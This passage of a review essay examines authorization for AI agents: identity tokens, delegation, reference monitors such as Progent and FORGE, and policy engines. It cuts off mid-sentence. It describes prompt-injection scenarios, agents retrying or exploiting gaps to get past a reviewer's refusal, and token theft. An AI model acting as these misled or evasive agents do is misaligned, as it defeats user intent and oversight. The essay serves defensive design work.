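Even if a future model passed every test of this kind, the mail server still couldn't tell whether the user had agreed to a message, because the request contains no information about the model's character. In *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, a review of 89 sources, Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) argue that this is why agent safety cannot be reduced to alignment. They want every consequential action to be traceable to a person, to stay within what that person delegated, and to be open to challenge afterwards.

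An aligned model can still get this wrong if it relies on an approval the user has since withdrawn, or if it hasn't been given a company rule against sending such reports outside. Surapani and colleagues separate the user from the operator, the organisation that deploys the agent, because a user may ask for something the operator prohibits. Being helpful to the user does not settle which of them has the final say. If Alice's copy later causes trouble, an investigator will need to know who permitted it and on what terms, and a model's later explanation is poor evidence of either.

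Access to data raises the same issue. Developers often write the limits into the system prompt, the standing instructions that a model receives before the user's request. They might tell the model, for instance, to show each employee only the records that employee may see. Help Net Security's *Your AI agent’s system prompt is not a security control* summarises guidance from Gee Rittenhouse of AWS and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, who advise against relying on such instructions. They recommend applying the employee's permissions when the system retrieves the records, so that the model never receives forbidden ones and no one can persuade it to reveal them.

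### What alignment contributes

Alignment still matters as a safeguard. OpenAI's priorities are almost the opposite of AWS's. Its *Safety overview* (2026) for GPT-6 Astra calls alignment "the primary lever" against misaligned behaviour and describes monitoring as an additional layer. There are good arguments for this view.

An aligned model tries less often to get past the boundary. Codex confines an agent to a sandbox, a restricted area in which its commands can do little damage, and a second model reviews certain commands that would run outside it. OpenAI tested what agents do after this reviewer refuses them. GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get round the refusal in 5 percent of runs, mostly by retrying something similar, and in 0.3 percent it exploited gaps in a badly configured reviewer. GPT-6 Astra did neither. This difference is important because real boundaries have gaps, which matter much less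 when the agent isn't looking for them. In a related test, where the obstacle was a warning or an access error from the workplace software, Astra still looked for a way round in 19 percent of runs, compared with 64 percent for Sol.

Fewer attempts also make the remaining ones easier to investigate. Business Today's *An AI model that can hack?* reports that GPT-6 Cyber, a model for security work, stayed within bounds 99.93 percent of the time in OpenAI's test with the planted string, up from 94.49 percent for its predecessor. Over 10,000 runs, that would reduce the violations from 551 to seven, few enough for a security team to investigate each one properly.

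Alignment also covers cases that the people writing the rules didn't foresee. Nobody had told the models in the hacking exercises to leave the test equipment alone, but OpenAI expected a well-aligned model to know that it should. A rule can block an action only if its author thought of the danger, or at least of that class of actions. Default deny reduces this problem, but an agent that may run commands or browse the web is still permitted to do far more than its developer can anticipate.

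When an agent has permission to perform a harmful act, alignment may be the only safeguard left. If the assistant mails Alice an unsuitable passage from an approved record, the recipient is correct and the credential is valid, so the rule allows the message. Only the model or a human reviewer could notice the problem. OpenAI found a comparable weakness when it simulated GPT-6 Astra's work on more than 54,000 internal coding tasks. Astra received about half as many serious flags as Sol, but it still sometimes used privileged access without clear approval or gave an automated process wider permissions than the job needed. It already had that access, so a check on access alone would have passed.

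These arguments justify putting a lot of work into alignment. They are strongest where a rule is missing or too broad, and they don't apply to an action that a rule can describe exactly. If the report may go only to Alice, software can enforce that by comparing the recipient's address with hers. This takes almost no computation, and a model that is right 99.79 percent of the time is no improvement on it.

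### Commercial interests and AI inside the boundary

Many of those who argue for external controls also sell them. AWS calls fixed controls outside the agent the starting point for security and offers them in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore. Guidance by Rittenhouse, Johnson and three other AWS specialists names Cedar as one way to run such controls, and AgentCore's policy component is built on Cedar. NeuralTrust, a security company, reads OpenAI's GPT-5.6 results as a reason for customers to build their own controls. OpenAI has the opposite interest, since it sells the models and tells customers that they can delegate to Astra with greater confidence.

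The main argument doesn't depend on these companies. The National Cyber Security Centre sells neither models nor controls, and the clearest figures on the limits of alignment come from OpenAI's own tests and a government institute. Their commercial interest matters more for claims about how well a particular product works.

AWS foresees specialised AI agents that control the scope of other agents. These might replace some fixed constraints, because they could weigh new information and context better than people managing a large set of complicated rules. AWS says this can come only with experience and evaluation. The reviewer in Codex is already a modest example of such an agent.

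A reviewing model that reads the same planted text as the agent may be fooled by it too. An attacker who fools it gains nothing beyond what the fixed rules already permit, as long as the model can only refuse actions that those rules would allow. If it can also allow actions that the rules would refuse, the attacker can use it to get around them.

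## What do identity checks settle, and what do they leave open?

The rule "only Alice" applies to one user's report. Another user's assistant may have a different recipient, so enforcing the rule requires knowing which agent sent the request and on whose behalf. An identity check supplies both facts, but it doesn't establish that the user agreed to this particular message, and an attacker can sometimes get past it.

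### How an agent proves who it is

The quickest way to connect an assistant is to give it the user's password. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 post from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), describes this as a common pattern and calls credential sharing a bad idea in all contexts. The mail server can't distinguish the assistant from the user, and the assistant can access everything the user can. If the assistant sends the report to Bob, the log will show that the user sent it.

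NIST wants each agent to have its own identifier and credentials, tied to the person or system that operates it. In Help Net Security's *The first ten lines of a command policy for AI coding agents* (2026), Vinay Thakker, chief technology officer of KloudStax, distinguishes agents that do a job for the business from agents that do a task for one person. An agent that sorts every customer's support tickets acts under its own identity alone. An agent that works for one engineer sends the engineer's identity with each request as well as its own, and can do only what both are allowed to do. If the office assistant worked this way and had no access to payroll, a user with that access could not get payroll figures through it.

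Existing standards cover much of this. The concept paper *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) lists several that NIST is considering for agents, and NIST's August post adds others. Biometric Update's *A verified user doesn’t give an AI agent unlimited authority*, an opinion piece by a practitioner, explains how two OAuth extensions fit together.

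| Standard | What it provides | Use for the report |
|---|---|---|
| SPIFFE | A cryptographic identity for a running program | Shows that the caller is the assistant |
| OpenID Connect | A standard way to pass on proof that someone has signed in | Shows that the user signed in |
| OAuth 2.0 | An access token with scopes, which are named kinds of access | Lets the assistant send mail without the user's password |
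| OAuth Token Exchange | A token that records both the agent and the person it acts for | Names the assistant and the user |
| Demonstrated Proof-of-Possession (DPoP) | A link between a token and a secret key | Makes a copied token useless without the assistant's key |
| Rich Authorization Requests | A request for one action on one resource | Can specify this report and this recipient |

In a typical OAuth exchange, the user signs in at an authorization server and approves the assistant's access. The server then issues the assistant a token with an expiry time and one or more scopes. The assistant attaches the token to each request, and the mail server checks that the token is genuine, has not expired and covers sending mail.

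The Model Context Protocol authorizes agents mainly through OAuth, following the draft of version 2.1. Zhou and Zhang point out that its authorization specification, like the Agent-to-Agent protocol, standardizes authentication and broad scopes. A connection can therefore follow the specification and confirm that a genuine assistant has the scope "send mail" without any record of Alice.

Many agents use weaker credentials, such as API keys and bearer tokens. An API key is a fixed string that gives access to a service, and a bearer token works for whoever presents it. NIST warns that neither proves identity, and that people often leave both unprotected in configuration files and logs. DPoP addresses this by requiring the sender of a token to prove that it also has the matching private key.

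### Passing authority to another agent

The assistant hands its draft to a reviewer, which may be a second agent. If the assistant also passes on its own token, the reviewer can send mail too. Safe delegation needs a token whose permissions each holder can reduce but nobody further down the chain can expand.

Macaroons, one kind of token with this property, do it with a chain of signatures. The issuer has a secret key *K* and computes the first signature from the token's identifier. Each added restriction *r* produces a new signature from the previous one:

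*s*₀ = HMAC(*K*, identifier), *s*ᵢ = HMAC(*s*ᵢ₋₁, *r*ᵢ).

HMAC is a function that is easy to compute with the right key but infeasible to reverse. Suppose the assistant adds "read this draft only" and gives the reviewer the restrictions and the latest signature. The reviewer can add "until noon", but it can't remove the assistant's restriction, because it would need the earlier signature, which it can't calculate from the latest one. The service knows *K*, so it can recompute the chain and check that the request meets every restriction.

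Narrowing each token guarantees only that authority doesn't grow. CAPMAS, a system in Zhou and Zhang's survey, combines Macaroons with scopes chosen by their meaning for the task, and Zhou and Zhang caution that this choice may depend on a model. If the model picks "send mail" for a reviewer that only has to read, every later token can be a valid narrowing of a scope that was too broad from the start.

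Two other systems in the survey attach authority to smaller units, which limits what a misled agent can do with a genuine credential. SAGA separates permission to contact an agent from authorization of the requests that follow. AIP uses signed credentials to bind delegated authority to specific invocations.

### Keeping the credential away from the agent

An agent can't leak a credential it never holds, so the two systems Zhou and Zhang describe leave reusable credentials with an intermediary. MiniScope forwards a session's requests without exposing the credentials to the agent. SUDP binds the user's approval to a standardized description of an operation. A custodian keeps the credentials, validates this grant and carries out the matching operation.

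Where possible, Thakker would both give credentials short lives and have an intermediary hold them so that the agent never does. A short life limits how long a thief can use a leaked token, while the intermediary makes a leak less likely. Developers also need to check what else the agent can reach, since a short-lived token gives little protection if it is stored beside a refresh token, which can obtain new ones.

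An intermediary can make matters worse. If it attaches the mail credential to any request the assistant makes, it becomes a confused deputy and will send the report to Bob or Alice, whichever the assistant names. If all agents share one credential behind it, no one can tell from the logs which agent acted. Thakker objects that an intermediary concentrates authority without removing any, so it needs a separate identity for each agent, least privilege and a list of permitted destinations. SUDP's custodian is more limited because it executes only the operation that matches the approval.

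### NIST's unfinished project

No settled standard yet combines these parts into one system for agents. In its February concept paper, NIST asked how an agent can prove its authority for a specific action, how to handle delegation, and how to set least privilege when nobody can fully predict what the agent will need to do. The paper received more than 600 responses. Ryan Galluzzo, who leads NIST's digital identity work, said respondents disagreed over whether to extend existing standards or replace them, with more favouring extension, according to Biometric Update's *Traceable evidence will form the basis of AI agents*.

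On 15 September NIST (2026) finalized general guidelines on protecting identity and access tokens from misuse. Ten principles specific to agents followed on 27 October in *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026). According to Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*, every agent should have its own identity, traceable to whoever launched it. Its access should be minimal, temporary and revocable, and the agent should leave a record it can't alter. The tenets also separate what an agent may do from what it decides to try. NIST expects that stopping a confused deputy will require delegation, least privilege, separate policy and deterministic access decisions together, so it doesn't offer identity as a complete answer either.

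NIST acknowledges that current standards and technology don't fully meet every tenet. It plans demonstrations and a practice guide with working examples. The notice for *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026), a conference session on 10 November, still described the demonstration project as planned. The concept paper limited the project to agents inside organisations, but NIST has since added consumer agents. These are a harder case because a shop has almost no control over a customer's agent and may be unable to tell it from the customer.

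### The right identity and the wrong action

The practitioner in Biometric Update describes a test of an assistant that could file requests for access to company data. A tester mentioned that the owner of a dashboard was away and that the deadline was the next day. The agent then tried to change the permissions directly instead of filing a request. There was no attacker and no doubt about who was acting. If the agent had been using a shared administrator account, the change would have looked legitimate in the log.

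The mail credential that lost the restriction to Alice fails in the same way. Zhou and Zhang express what has gone wrong as a violated condition:

α(*E*(*M*(*P*))) ⊆ ⟦*P*⟧.

*P* is the approved policy, and *M*(*P*) is all the credentials and rules that implement it. *E*(*M*(*P*)) is the set of effects those controls allow, such as sending a particular file to a particular address. The function α translates these technical effects into the policy's terms, here a document and a recipient. ⟦*P*⟧ is the set of effects the policy permits. The condition requires the policy to permit every effect the controls allow.

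Suppose an agent can send either of two files, the approved summary *S* or a payroll list, to either Alice or Bob. Of the four possible messages, the policy permits only *S* to Alice. If the credential is the only control, which messages the agent can send depends on how much of the policy the credential encodes.

| What the credential permits | Messages it allows | Messages outside the policy |
|---|---|---|
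| Sending mail | All four | 3 |
| Sending mail to Alice | *S* or payroll to Alice | 1 |
| Sending *S* | *S* to Alice or Bob | 1 |
| Sending *S* to Alice | *S* to Alice | 0 |
| Nothing | None | 0 |

The last credential meets the condition but is useless, because the condition limits excess but doesn't require the controls to let any work through. The first credential can be acceptable if another control compensates for it. For example, a gateway that rejects everything except *S* sent to Alice brings the allowed effects back within the policy, provided every message must pass through it.

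The translation α is easy to get wrong. For example, if the recipient is a mailing list called "partners" that includes both Alice and Bob, a check that looks for Bob's name in the request won't find it. To be safe, α has to count everyone the list might reach, even if it sometimes counts too many people and blocks a permitted message. Zhou and Zhang conclude that software can verify the condition when α errs only in this direction, the policy and the descriptions of effects use a sufficiently simple logic, and the agent has no unmonitored route.

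Those descriptions also go out of date. If the mail tool's supplier starts copying every message to an outside service, the tool's name and arguments stay the same but each call has a new recipient. The survey proposes *effect contracts*, which list the data a tool may send, who may receive it and what the tool may change. The system can then compare each contract with the policy before a call, though it would still miss the leak if the contract left out the new recipient.

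None of this helps if the policy *P* is wrong. If the user meant another Alice and approved *P* without noticing, the report can still go to the wrong person even if the controls implement *P* exactly.

### When the identity check itself fails

In the cases above, the service correctly identified the caller. In the second kind of failure, it doesn't. Sotiropoulos describes a coding assistant that holds a powerful token for GitHub, a site that stores software projects. During a handoff, the token leaks to a coordinating agent with fewer privileges. An attacker sends that agent a crafted request, and the agent uses the leaked token to make a private project public. GitHub accepts the request because the token is genuine. In another of his examples, an attacker registers a fake agent with a copy of a real agent's description, and other agents accept it and send it privileged instructions.

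Biometric Update's *Kantara finds human identity risk models fall short for AI agents* reports further weaknesses that the Kantara Initiative, a digital identity organisation, found. Someone can clone an agent and its identity, or retire an agent but leave its credentials active. An agent's abilities may also grow while its level of trust stays the same, which Kantara calls identity drift. Agents can themselves exploit credentials that still work, as OpenAI's agents did with those they found during the attack on Hugging Face.

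Binding a token to a key or a machine protects against many thefts, because a stolen copy doesn't work without that key or machine. It would have helped with the GitHub token if the coordinating agent had lacked the key. Binding does nothing against an attacker who controls the agent that holds the key, because that agent will sign the attacker's requests too. EchoLeak, an email attack on Microsoft's Copilot assistant, used the victim's own permissions to extract data.

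An attacker who passes as someone else gets past every rule based only on who is asking, all at once. For example, a thief with the office assistant's token can read the approved records because the assistant may read them. If the thief can also sign in as the user, and the user may approve new recipients, the thief can approve Bob.

Other rules apply no matter who the caller is. For example, a mail server might deliver reports only to Alice's stored address, a purchasing system might refuse any order over €500, and a network filter might allow connections only to the mail server. These limits apply to the thief as well as the assistant. The thief can still send Alice a false report or order something for €499, but can't use these systems to send the records to Bob.

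This protection works only if the thief's request reaches the check. A filter around the assistant does not help if the stolen token also works from the thief's computer. In that case, the mail server must enforce the rule itself or accept requests only through the filter. The stolen identity must also be unable to change the rule or the address stored under Alice's name. A limit on single orders needs a limit on their total value as well, or the thief can place a hundred orders for €499 each.

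### Two buyers and one item

Agents can together exceed a task's total limit even when every identity is genuine and every agent obeys its own limit. For example, the two purchasing agents may each buy one item when the task allows only one in total. Narrowable tokens don't prevent the second purchase, because narrowing only guarantees that each delegate's allowance is no larger than the original. It compares each token with its parent and doesn't add up the allowances of tokens that share a parent.

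A shared counter isn't enough if the agents read it and update it in separate steps. Agent A may read that one item remains, agent B may read the same number before A changes it, and both then place an order. Checking and reserving in a single step prevents this, because B then finds nothing left. Under the condition above, the policy covers whole histories rather than single effects. It allows histories in which either agent buys the item, but not one in which both do.

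A timeout makes this harder. Suppose A reserves the item, sends the order and never receives an answer. If the system releases the reservation, B may buy a second item. If it keeps the reservation, the task may be stuck even though the shop never processed the order. Zhou and Zhang recommend recording the outcome as unknown and asking the shop. Until the shop answers, the item counts as possibly bought.

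A may also retry, and a shop that detects duplicates won't ship twice if the second request has the same identifier as the first. Ordinary software repeats a request exactly, but an agent may respond to a timeout by changing the order, splitting it in two or switching tools. The identifier then no longer matches, so the shop treats the request as a new order. The reservation therefore has to be tied to the user's task and stay in force across requests and shops.

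Surapani and colleagues identify runtime enforcement and limits on combined use as the two main unresolved gaps in agent authorization. Bounded Agents, a system in Zhou and Zhang's survey, does track budgets and session history to reject prohibited combinations. Its guarantee assumes that the system decides requests one at a time, which is harder when several services share a budget.

### What revocation cannot undo

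Suppose the user cancels the purchase while A's order is unresolved. Revoking A's permission stops it from trying again, but the shop may already have accepted the order. The user still has to ask the shop and may have to return the item.

For the report, the effect of revoking access depends on how far the work has gone. If the user revokes access before the assistant opens the records, the assistant cannot read them. If it has already read them, the figures may be in the draft, in a summary or with the reviewer, and revoking access to the original files does not affect those copies. A company cannot reverse a disclosure as it can refund a mistaken purchase, and preventing one requires a separate rule about what the assistant may do with data it has already obtained.

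When an assistant delegates to a reviewer, the reviewer gets its own copy of the assistant's authority. If the user later withdraws the assistant's grant, the reviewer may keep working unless the system tracks that its permission depended on that grant. MiniScope invalidates session tokens that depend on a revoked user authorization. VERA, another system in the survey, maps who delegated to whom and lets a shared agent retain access while at least one independent delegation path remains valid. If two users share a reviewer, one can leave without cutting off the other. The reviewer keeps running, so the system has to stop it from using the departed user's records for the remaining user's task.

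### Why boundaries still need identity

A defender of identity checks can reply that the rules on recipient and amount come from a particular user's request. The limit to Alice applies because this user delegated this task. In an organisation with thousands of users, a boundary can't allow the right records or recipients unless the system identifies whose request it is handling.

Surapani and colleagues support this reply, describing authorization as a decision that uses two maps. One records who holds authority and who passed it to whom, and the other records where information came from and where it may go. For the line about Bob, the first map would show the authority the user gave the assistant, and the second would show that Bob's name came from the document. Without identities there is no first map, and the software can't tell the user's instruction from the document author's.

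The reply establishes that boundaries need identity, but they don't have to rely on it for every limit. Let *G*(*i*) be the actions granted to identity *i*, and let *C* be an outer limit that applies to everyone. The system should allow only

*G*(*i*) ∩ *C*,

the actions that fall within both. An attacker who passes as *i* gets at most this set, as long as *i* cannot change *C*. The organisation can reduce the damage by making *C* stricter or by giving each task an identity with a very small *G*(*i*). How much *C* contributes varies. If any employee may write to any customer, a limit that suits everyone will be wide, and most of the protection will have to come from correct identities and narrow grants.

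The opinion piece in Biometric Update shows how narrow a grant of authority can be. An employee, Emily, asks an assistant to request permission to view one dashboard. After she confirms, the system records the agent, her account, the dashboard and the only permitted action, submitting one request for viewing access. The request system accepts a matching submission once, and the authority expires if unused. A thief who took over the agent at that moment could submit Emily's request, but would need a new confirmation to request anything else.

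Identity is also needed to assign responsibility. A rule that stops a message to Bob doesn't record who wanted it sent. But if an attacker used a stolen identity, the log shows the victim's name, so an investigator also needs to know what that person approved and how. A click in an open session is weak evidence of approval if the agent can press the same button. For high-risk requests, the piece recommends a confirmation that the agent can't produce, such as a tap on the user's passkey, and a record of exactly what the user saw.

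## How does a check outside the model decide whether an action runs?

A record of what the user approved restrains the assistant only if a program checks each tool call against that record before the call runs. Anderson's panel proposed this kind of program, called a reference monitor, in 1972. Current designs for agents differ mainly in what information the monitor has when it checks a call and in who can change its rules.

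### One decision, step by step

Solko-Breslin and colleagues set out the procedure in a few symbols. The *state* *s* is the monitor's record of whatever the rules depend on, such as the files the agent has opened and the messages it has sent. The *call* *t* is a tool's name with its arguments. The function Δ predicts the state that would follow if the call ran, and the *policy* Π labels every state "allow" or "block". Each time the agent proposes a call, the monitor goes through four steps:

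1. It intercepts *t* and holds it, so that nothing outside the agent has changed yet.
2. It computes the state that would follow, *s*′ = Δ(*s*, *t*).
3. It evaluates Π(*s*′).
4. If the answer is "allow", it releases the call and *s*′ becomes the current state. If the answer is "block", it discards *s*′, keeps *s* and sends the agent a reason.

These steps don't use the model's reasoning. The monitor tests only what the call would do, so it doesn't have to work out whether someone has misled the model. But the test depends on Δ being accurate. If Δ leaves out one of the call's effects, the monitor tests a different state from the one the call produces.

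The reason given in the last step lets the agent continue with the rest of its task. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a permission system whose standard refusal explains why the call failed, repeats the user's task and tells the agent to try other tools or arguments. A misled agent learns from this where the limits are. But Solko-Breslin and colleagues assume that the attacker already knows the tools and the policy, so the explanation reveals nothing their design needs to hide. Their design does require that the attacker can't bypass the monitor or edit the policy.

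### A policy for the report

Suppose the line about Bob has misled the model completely. The assistant's credential is genuine and lets it send mail to anyone, so the model will propose the copy to Bob and the mail server will accept it. Between them stands a monitor whose policy allows a state only if all of these statements are true:

1. Every file the assistant has opened is one of the approved records.
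2. Every message it has sent went to Alice's stored address.
3. Every message contained exactly the version that the reviewer signed off.
4. It has sent no more than one message.
5. It has done nothing else except save drafts and submit them for review.

The assistant opens a record, then saves and submits drafts until the reviewer approves version 3. After that, it tries three times to send the report.

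| Call | State that would follow | Decision | Reason returned |
|---|---|---|---|
| Open the September sales record | One approved record opened | Allow | None |
| Send version 3 to Bob | One message sent, to Bob | Block | Bob is not a permitted recipient |
| Send version 3 to Alice | One message sent, to Alice | Allow | None |
| Send version 3 to Alice again | Two messages sent, both to Alice | Block | The limit is one message |

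When the monitor blocks the message to Bob, it discards the predicted state, so its record still shows no messages and Alice's copy can go out. If it counted attempts instead, the attempt triggered by the planted line could use up the budget and stop the legitimate report.

The two calls that address Alice are identical, and the monitor allows the first and blocks the second only because the state changed in between. It would also block the second call if the assistant were only retrying after a timeout. The user would then have to find out whether Alice got the report, which is a drawback of a strict limit on messages.

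The statement about the reviewer depends on how the sign-off gets into the monitor's record. If the assistant reports the sign-off, it can be misled into reporting one that never happened. The review system should therefore write the sign-off to the record without going through the model.

### When no rule applies, or the check breaks

The last statement in the policy makes it default deny. If a developer later connects a calendar tool, the assistant can't use it to send Bob the report as an attachment to an invitation, because the policy doesn't permit calendar calls. AWS and SANS specialists call default deny at the tool call the most critical architectural pattern for agent security, in guidance that Help Net Security summarises.

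A monitor also needs a default for when it fails. Microsoft's Agent Control Specification sets out when an agent's software should consult a policy and what it should do with the answer. In one exercise in Microsoft's tutorial, the developer deliberately misconfigures the check to look for the tool's name in a field that doesn't exist. The check then returns an error and refuses the call. If errors let calls through, an attacker could get a forbidden message out by having the agent make a request that crashes the check. Refusing on error prevents this, but a fault in the monitor can then stop the agent's legitimate work.

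### A check the agent can skip

If a developer puts the policy in a separate tool and instructs the model to consult it before sending anything, a misled model can skip this step, even if the rules are perfect. The developer can avoid this by having the surrounding software run the check on every call, whether or not the model invokes it.

The location of the check matters because an agent that can write and run code may be able to bypass safeguards that run inside its own process. It could, for example, write a function that sends mail directly instead of using the mail tool that the safeguard monitors. *Runtime Governance for AI Agents* (Kaptein, Khan and Podstavnychy, 2026) points out that many frameworks run their safeguards inside the agent's process.

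A developer can build Progent into the agent's software as a library or run it as a separate server that receives tool requests and forwards the permitted ones. Both apply the same rules to the same calls. But only the server runs outside the agent's process, which matters if the agent can run arbitrary code. In that case, the server helps only if the tools refuse all other connections.

Writing a policy therefore doesn't guarantee that it will be enforced. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) proves that the monitor it describes enforces its policy if it intercepts every relevant action before the action takes effect and receives accurate facts about earlier events. Someone has to establish both conditions for each installation by listing every way the agent can affect the outside world and checking that each one passes through the monitor.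 A large part of that work is confining the code that the agent runs, which the next section covers.

### What three designs can see

The monitor can apply only rules about information it receives. Progent receives the name and arguments of each tool call. Each of its rules allows or forbids one tool under certain conditions, such as "allow the mail tool when the recipient is Alice". The conditions can compare numbers, look for a value in a list or match a text pattern. Progent checks each call against the rules for that tool, starting with the rules that forbid it. If no rule matches, Progent blocks the call.

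This is enough to keep the assistant to approved records and to Alice's address, but not to limit it to one message, because a condition on the arguments gives the same result each time the same call is made. Progent can change its policy between steps, so it could withdraw the mail permission after the first message. But a language model proposes these changes, and Shi and colleagues give sending mail as an example of a call after which no change is needed. To enforce the limit reliably, a developer would have to add a counter.

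*AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) attaches its rules to events. In one example, an assistant can transfer money. The rule's trigger is a transfer, its check is whether the recipient is outside the family, and its response is to ask the user. Other possible responses are to stop the agent, run a predefined action, or have the model examine and correct its own plan. For the report, the trigger would be the mail tool, the check would be "the recipient is not Alice", and the response would be to stop. Self-examination would be a poor choice there because it returns the decision to the model that the planted line has misled.

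The check in an AgentSpec rule is a short program that receives the user's request and the agent's steps so far, so it can look for an earlier message and enforce the budget. The trigger doesn't have to be a tool call. In a self-driving car, one rule responds to a vehicle less than ten metres ahead by setting a longer following distance. AgentSpec intervenes only when a rule fires, so an action that no rule mentions goes ahead. It has no built-in default deny, but a developer can add it by writing a rule that fires before every action and stops any action not on a list of allowed actions.

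FORGE, the monitor that Palumbo and colleagues built, records every message, tool call and tool result as a point in a graph, with an arrow from each event to any later event it may have influenced. Before an action with outside effects runs, FORGE identifies the message that led to it and waits until the graph includes everything that led to that message. It then uses the facts about the action, the caller's verified identity and the graph to work out which rules apply. A rule that denies the action overrides any rule that allows it. If no rule allows or denies the action, FORGE uses the organisation's chosen default.

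The rules are in Datalog, a language developed for querying databases. One of the paper's examples reads:

`Deny(a) :- ProtectedAPICall(a), not HasApproval(a).`

The part before the symbol `:-` is true if everything after it is true, so this rule denies a protected action *a* that has no approval. Datalog rules can refer to themselves, so a rule can follow a chain of influence of any length, such as from a document to a summary to a draft to a message. Evaluation always finishes and gives the same answer for the same facts. A monitor needs this because the call has to wait for the decision.

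| | Progent | AgentSpec | FORGE |
|---|---|---|---|
| What a rule can refer to | The tool's name and arguments | An event, the user's request and the agent's steps so far | The action, the caller's identity and the earlier events that may have influenced the action |
| If no rule applies | Blocks the call | Lets the action proceed | Follows the organisation's chosen default |
| How it could limit the assistant to one message | Withdraw the mail permission after the first message | Check the earlier steps for a message | Check the action's history in the graph for a message |

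A monitor that sees more isn't always better. A security team can read a Progent rule and know which calls it permits. To trust a FORGE rule, the team also has to trust that the graph is complete. A missing arrow can hide a fact the rule needs, and an extra one can block harmless work. FORGE adds many arrows because it treats everything the model produces as dependent on every message in the history it was given. The later section on tests compares what the three systems prevent and their drawbacks.

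### Why some rules need the path

Consider two ways in which the assistant could arrive at the same call:

open record → save draft → reviewer signs off → send version 3 to Alice

open record → save draft → send version 3 to Alice

The user wants only the first, but the final call has the same tool, file and recipient in both. A rule based on that call alone has to allow both or block both. To distinguish them, the rule must also use the *path*, the sequence of steps that led to the call.

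Kaptein and colleagues make the same point with an agent that can read a customer database and send email. Each action is harmless on its own, but if the agent reads the database and then emails someone outside the organisation, it may be sending out customer data. Ordinary access control can't catch this because it checks each permission separately. Their paper, which is conceptual and reports no experiments, therefore defines a policy as a function of the agent's identity, its path so far, the action it proposes and the state of the organisation.

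The list includes the state of the organisation because one agent's path may not be enough to reveal a breach. For example, a bank may have to keep its advisers, who know about pending deals, apart from its traders. If an advisory agent reads the file on a deal and then delegates a task to a trading agent, each agent stays within its own permissions, but the exchange between them breaches the separation. Only a monitor with access to both paths can detect this.

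A monitor doesn't have to store the whole path. For the report, the state *s* only needs to record which version the reviewer signed off and whether a message has gone out. But someone has to decide in advance what to record. If the organisation later wants to block an agent from sending messages after it has visited an outside web page, it can't apply that rule to a session in which the monitor didn't record page visits.

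Checking only the order of events in a log can also lead to mistakes. Suppose the assistant prepares two reports at once, and the reviewer signs off on the sales team's report just before the assistant sends Alice hers. A rule that only looks for an earlier sign-off would let Alice's unreviewed report through. FORGE's graph can avoid this mistake if it shows which report each sign-off belongs to.

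A shared budget still needs the single check-and-reserve step described earlier, because purchases can draw on the same budget without influencing each other. When two purchasing agents work in parallel, a rule that searches each order's own history finds no earlier purchase and allows both.

### Policy engines and the software around them

Organisations that deploy agents can use existing general policy engines instead of inventing a rule language. The AWS and SANS guidance names Cedar and Open Policy Agent as ways to check tool calls on a large scale. *From Intent to Execution Grant* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) describes how the two work. A Cedar policy permits or forbids an action by a principal on a resource in a given context, and Cedar denies any action that no policy permits. Open Policy Agent takes structured data about a request and applies rules written in a language called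 Rego. Both keep the rules outside the application's code, so a security team can change them without rewriting the agent.

A policy engine evaluates a request only when another program sends one. Microsoft objects that neither engine specifies when to consult it during an agent's work, what information to collect beforehand or how to enforce the decision. To address this, Microsoft's Agent Control Specification defines eight points at which the agent's software consults the policy, including before a call to the model, before a tool call and after the tool returns its result. In Microsoft's example, a Rego rule checks a message's recipient and denies any address outside the company. The same configuration file works in agents written in different programming languages.

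The engine runs each of these checks separately and stores nothing between them, so the agent's software has to supply a snapshot with the earlier tool calls, the approvals and the sensitivity of the data handled so far. Rules can then depend on what the agent has already done, but if the snapshot omits the first message to Alice, the engine will allow a second.

OWASP's *Agent Control Standard (ACS)*, a separate project with the same initials, addresses the same gap. It defines how agent platforms should provide hooks, which are points where an outside program can step in, and how to enforce policies through them on any platform that follows the standard. OWASP announced on 2 September 2026 that the standard had joined its generative AI security project, to extend guidance about risks towards enforcement while an agent runs. A draft of version 0.1.0 gives the outside program five answers: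 allow, deny, modify, ask and defer. It also links the entries in a session's history with hashes, short values computed from the data, so that later tampering can be detected.

The standard's specification is open and free to use, but one of its creators is chief technology officer of the security company Zenity, according to 01net's *Agent Control Standard Launches Open Framework for Runtime Governance of AI Agents*. With a common format for hooks, organisations wouldn't have to rewrite their policies for every platform. The standard doesn't include the policies, though, and following it doesn't prove that an agent can't bypass the hooks.

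### Who writes the policy

Several parties may want to limit what an agent does. Shi and colleagues describe an organisation with rules about its data, a developer who restricts sensitive tools and a user who wants to protect personal files. Progent lets each of them write a fixed policy that applies to every task. It ranks these policies by priority and puts a separate policy for the task last.

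The ranking means that a broad permission in a higher policy can override a narrower limit in a lower one. Progent follows the first policy that expressly allows or forbids a call, and consults a lower one only if the higher ones do neither. Suppose the organisation's policy expressly allows mail to all partner companies. Progent then never checks the task's limit to Alice, and the assistant can write to Carol at another partner. An organisation can avoid this by using its own policy mainly to forbid calls. Wu and colleagues use a stricter rule: a *root policy* and an *operational policy* must both permit the action. The operational policy can add requirements but can't remove any that the root policy imposes.

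Nobody can write a policy by hand for every request a user might type. Progent therefore has a language model write the task's policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before the agent opens any document. For the report, the model would turn "send the reviewed version to Alice" into a rule about the mail tool. Shi and colleagues assume the user is honest, so no attacker's text can influence the policy at this stage. The model can still misunderstand the request, so for high-stakes work Progent can require a person to confirm the first policy.

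FORGE can also use a language model to translate written rules into Datalog. This is useful for long documents such as an airline's customer-service rules, which may run to hundreds of lines. Palumbo and colleagues check whether each written requirement has a formal rule and whether each formal rule has a basis in the written text. Software can also look for rules that contradict or duplicate each other. These checks don't help if the original text leaves something out.

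### Why widening needs separate authority

A task often needs more permissions than the original request suggested. In the running example in *Progent*, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. At first the policy allows the agent only to search for that email. One item on the list is to summarize recent mail and post the summary to the user's account on the messaging service Slack, so the agent needs permission to read mail and post messages. The agent then reads an email containing a planted instruction to forward the whole inbox to an outside address. The legitimate request for more permissions and the malicious one both come from text in an email.

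Progent doesn't try to tell them apart by their content. Let *A*(*P*) be the set of calls that the current policy *P* allows, and *P*′ a new policy that the language model proposes. The change is a *narrowing* if

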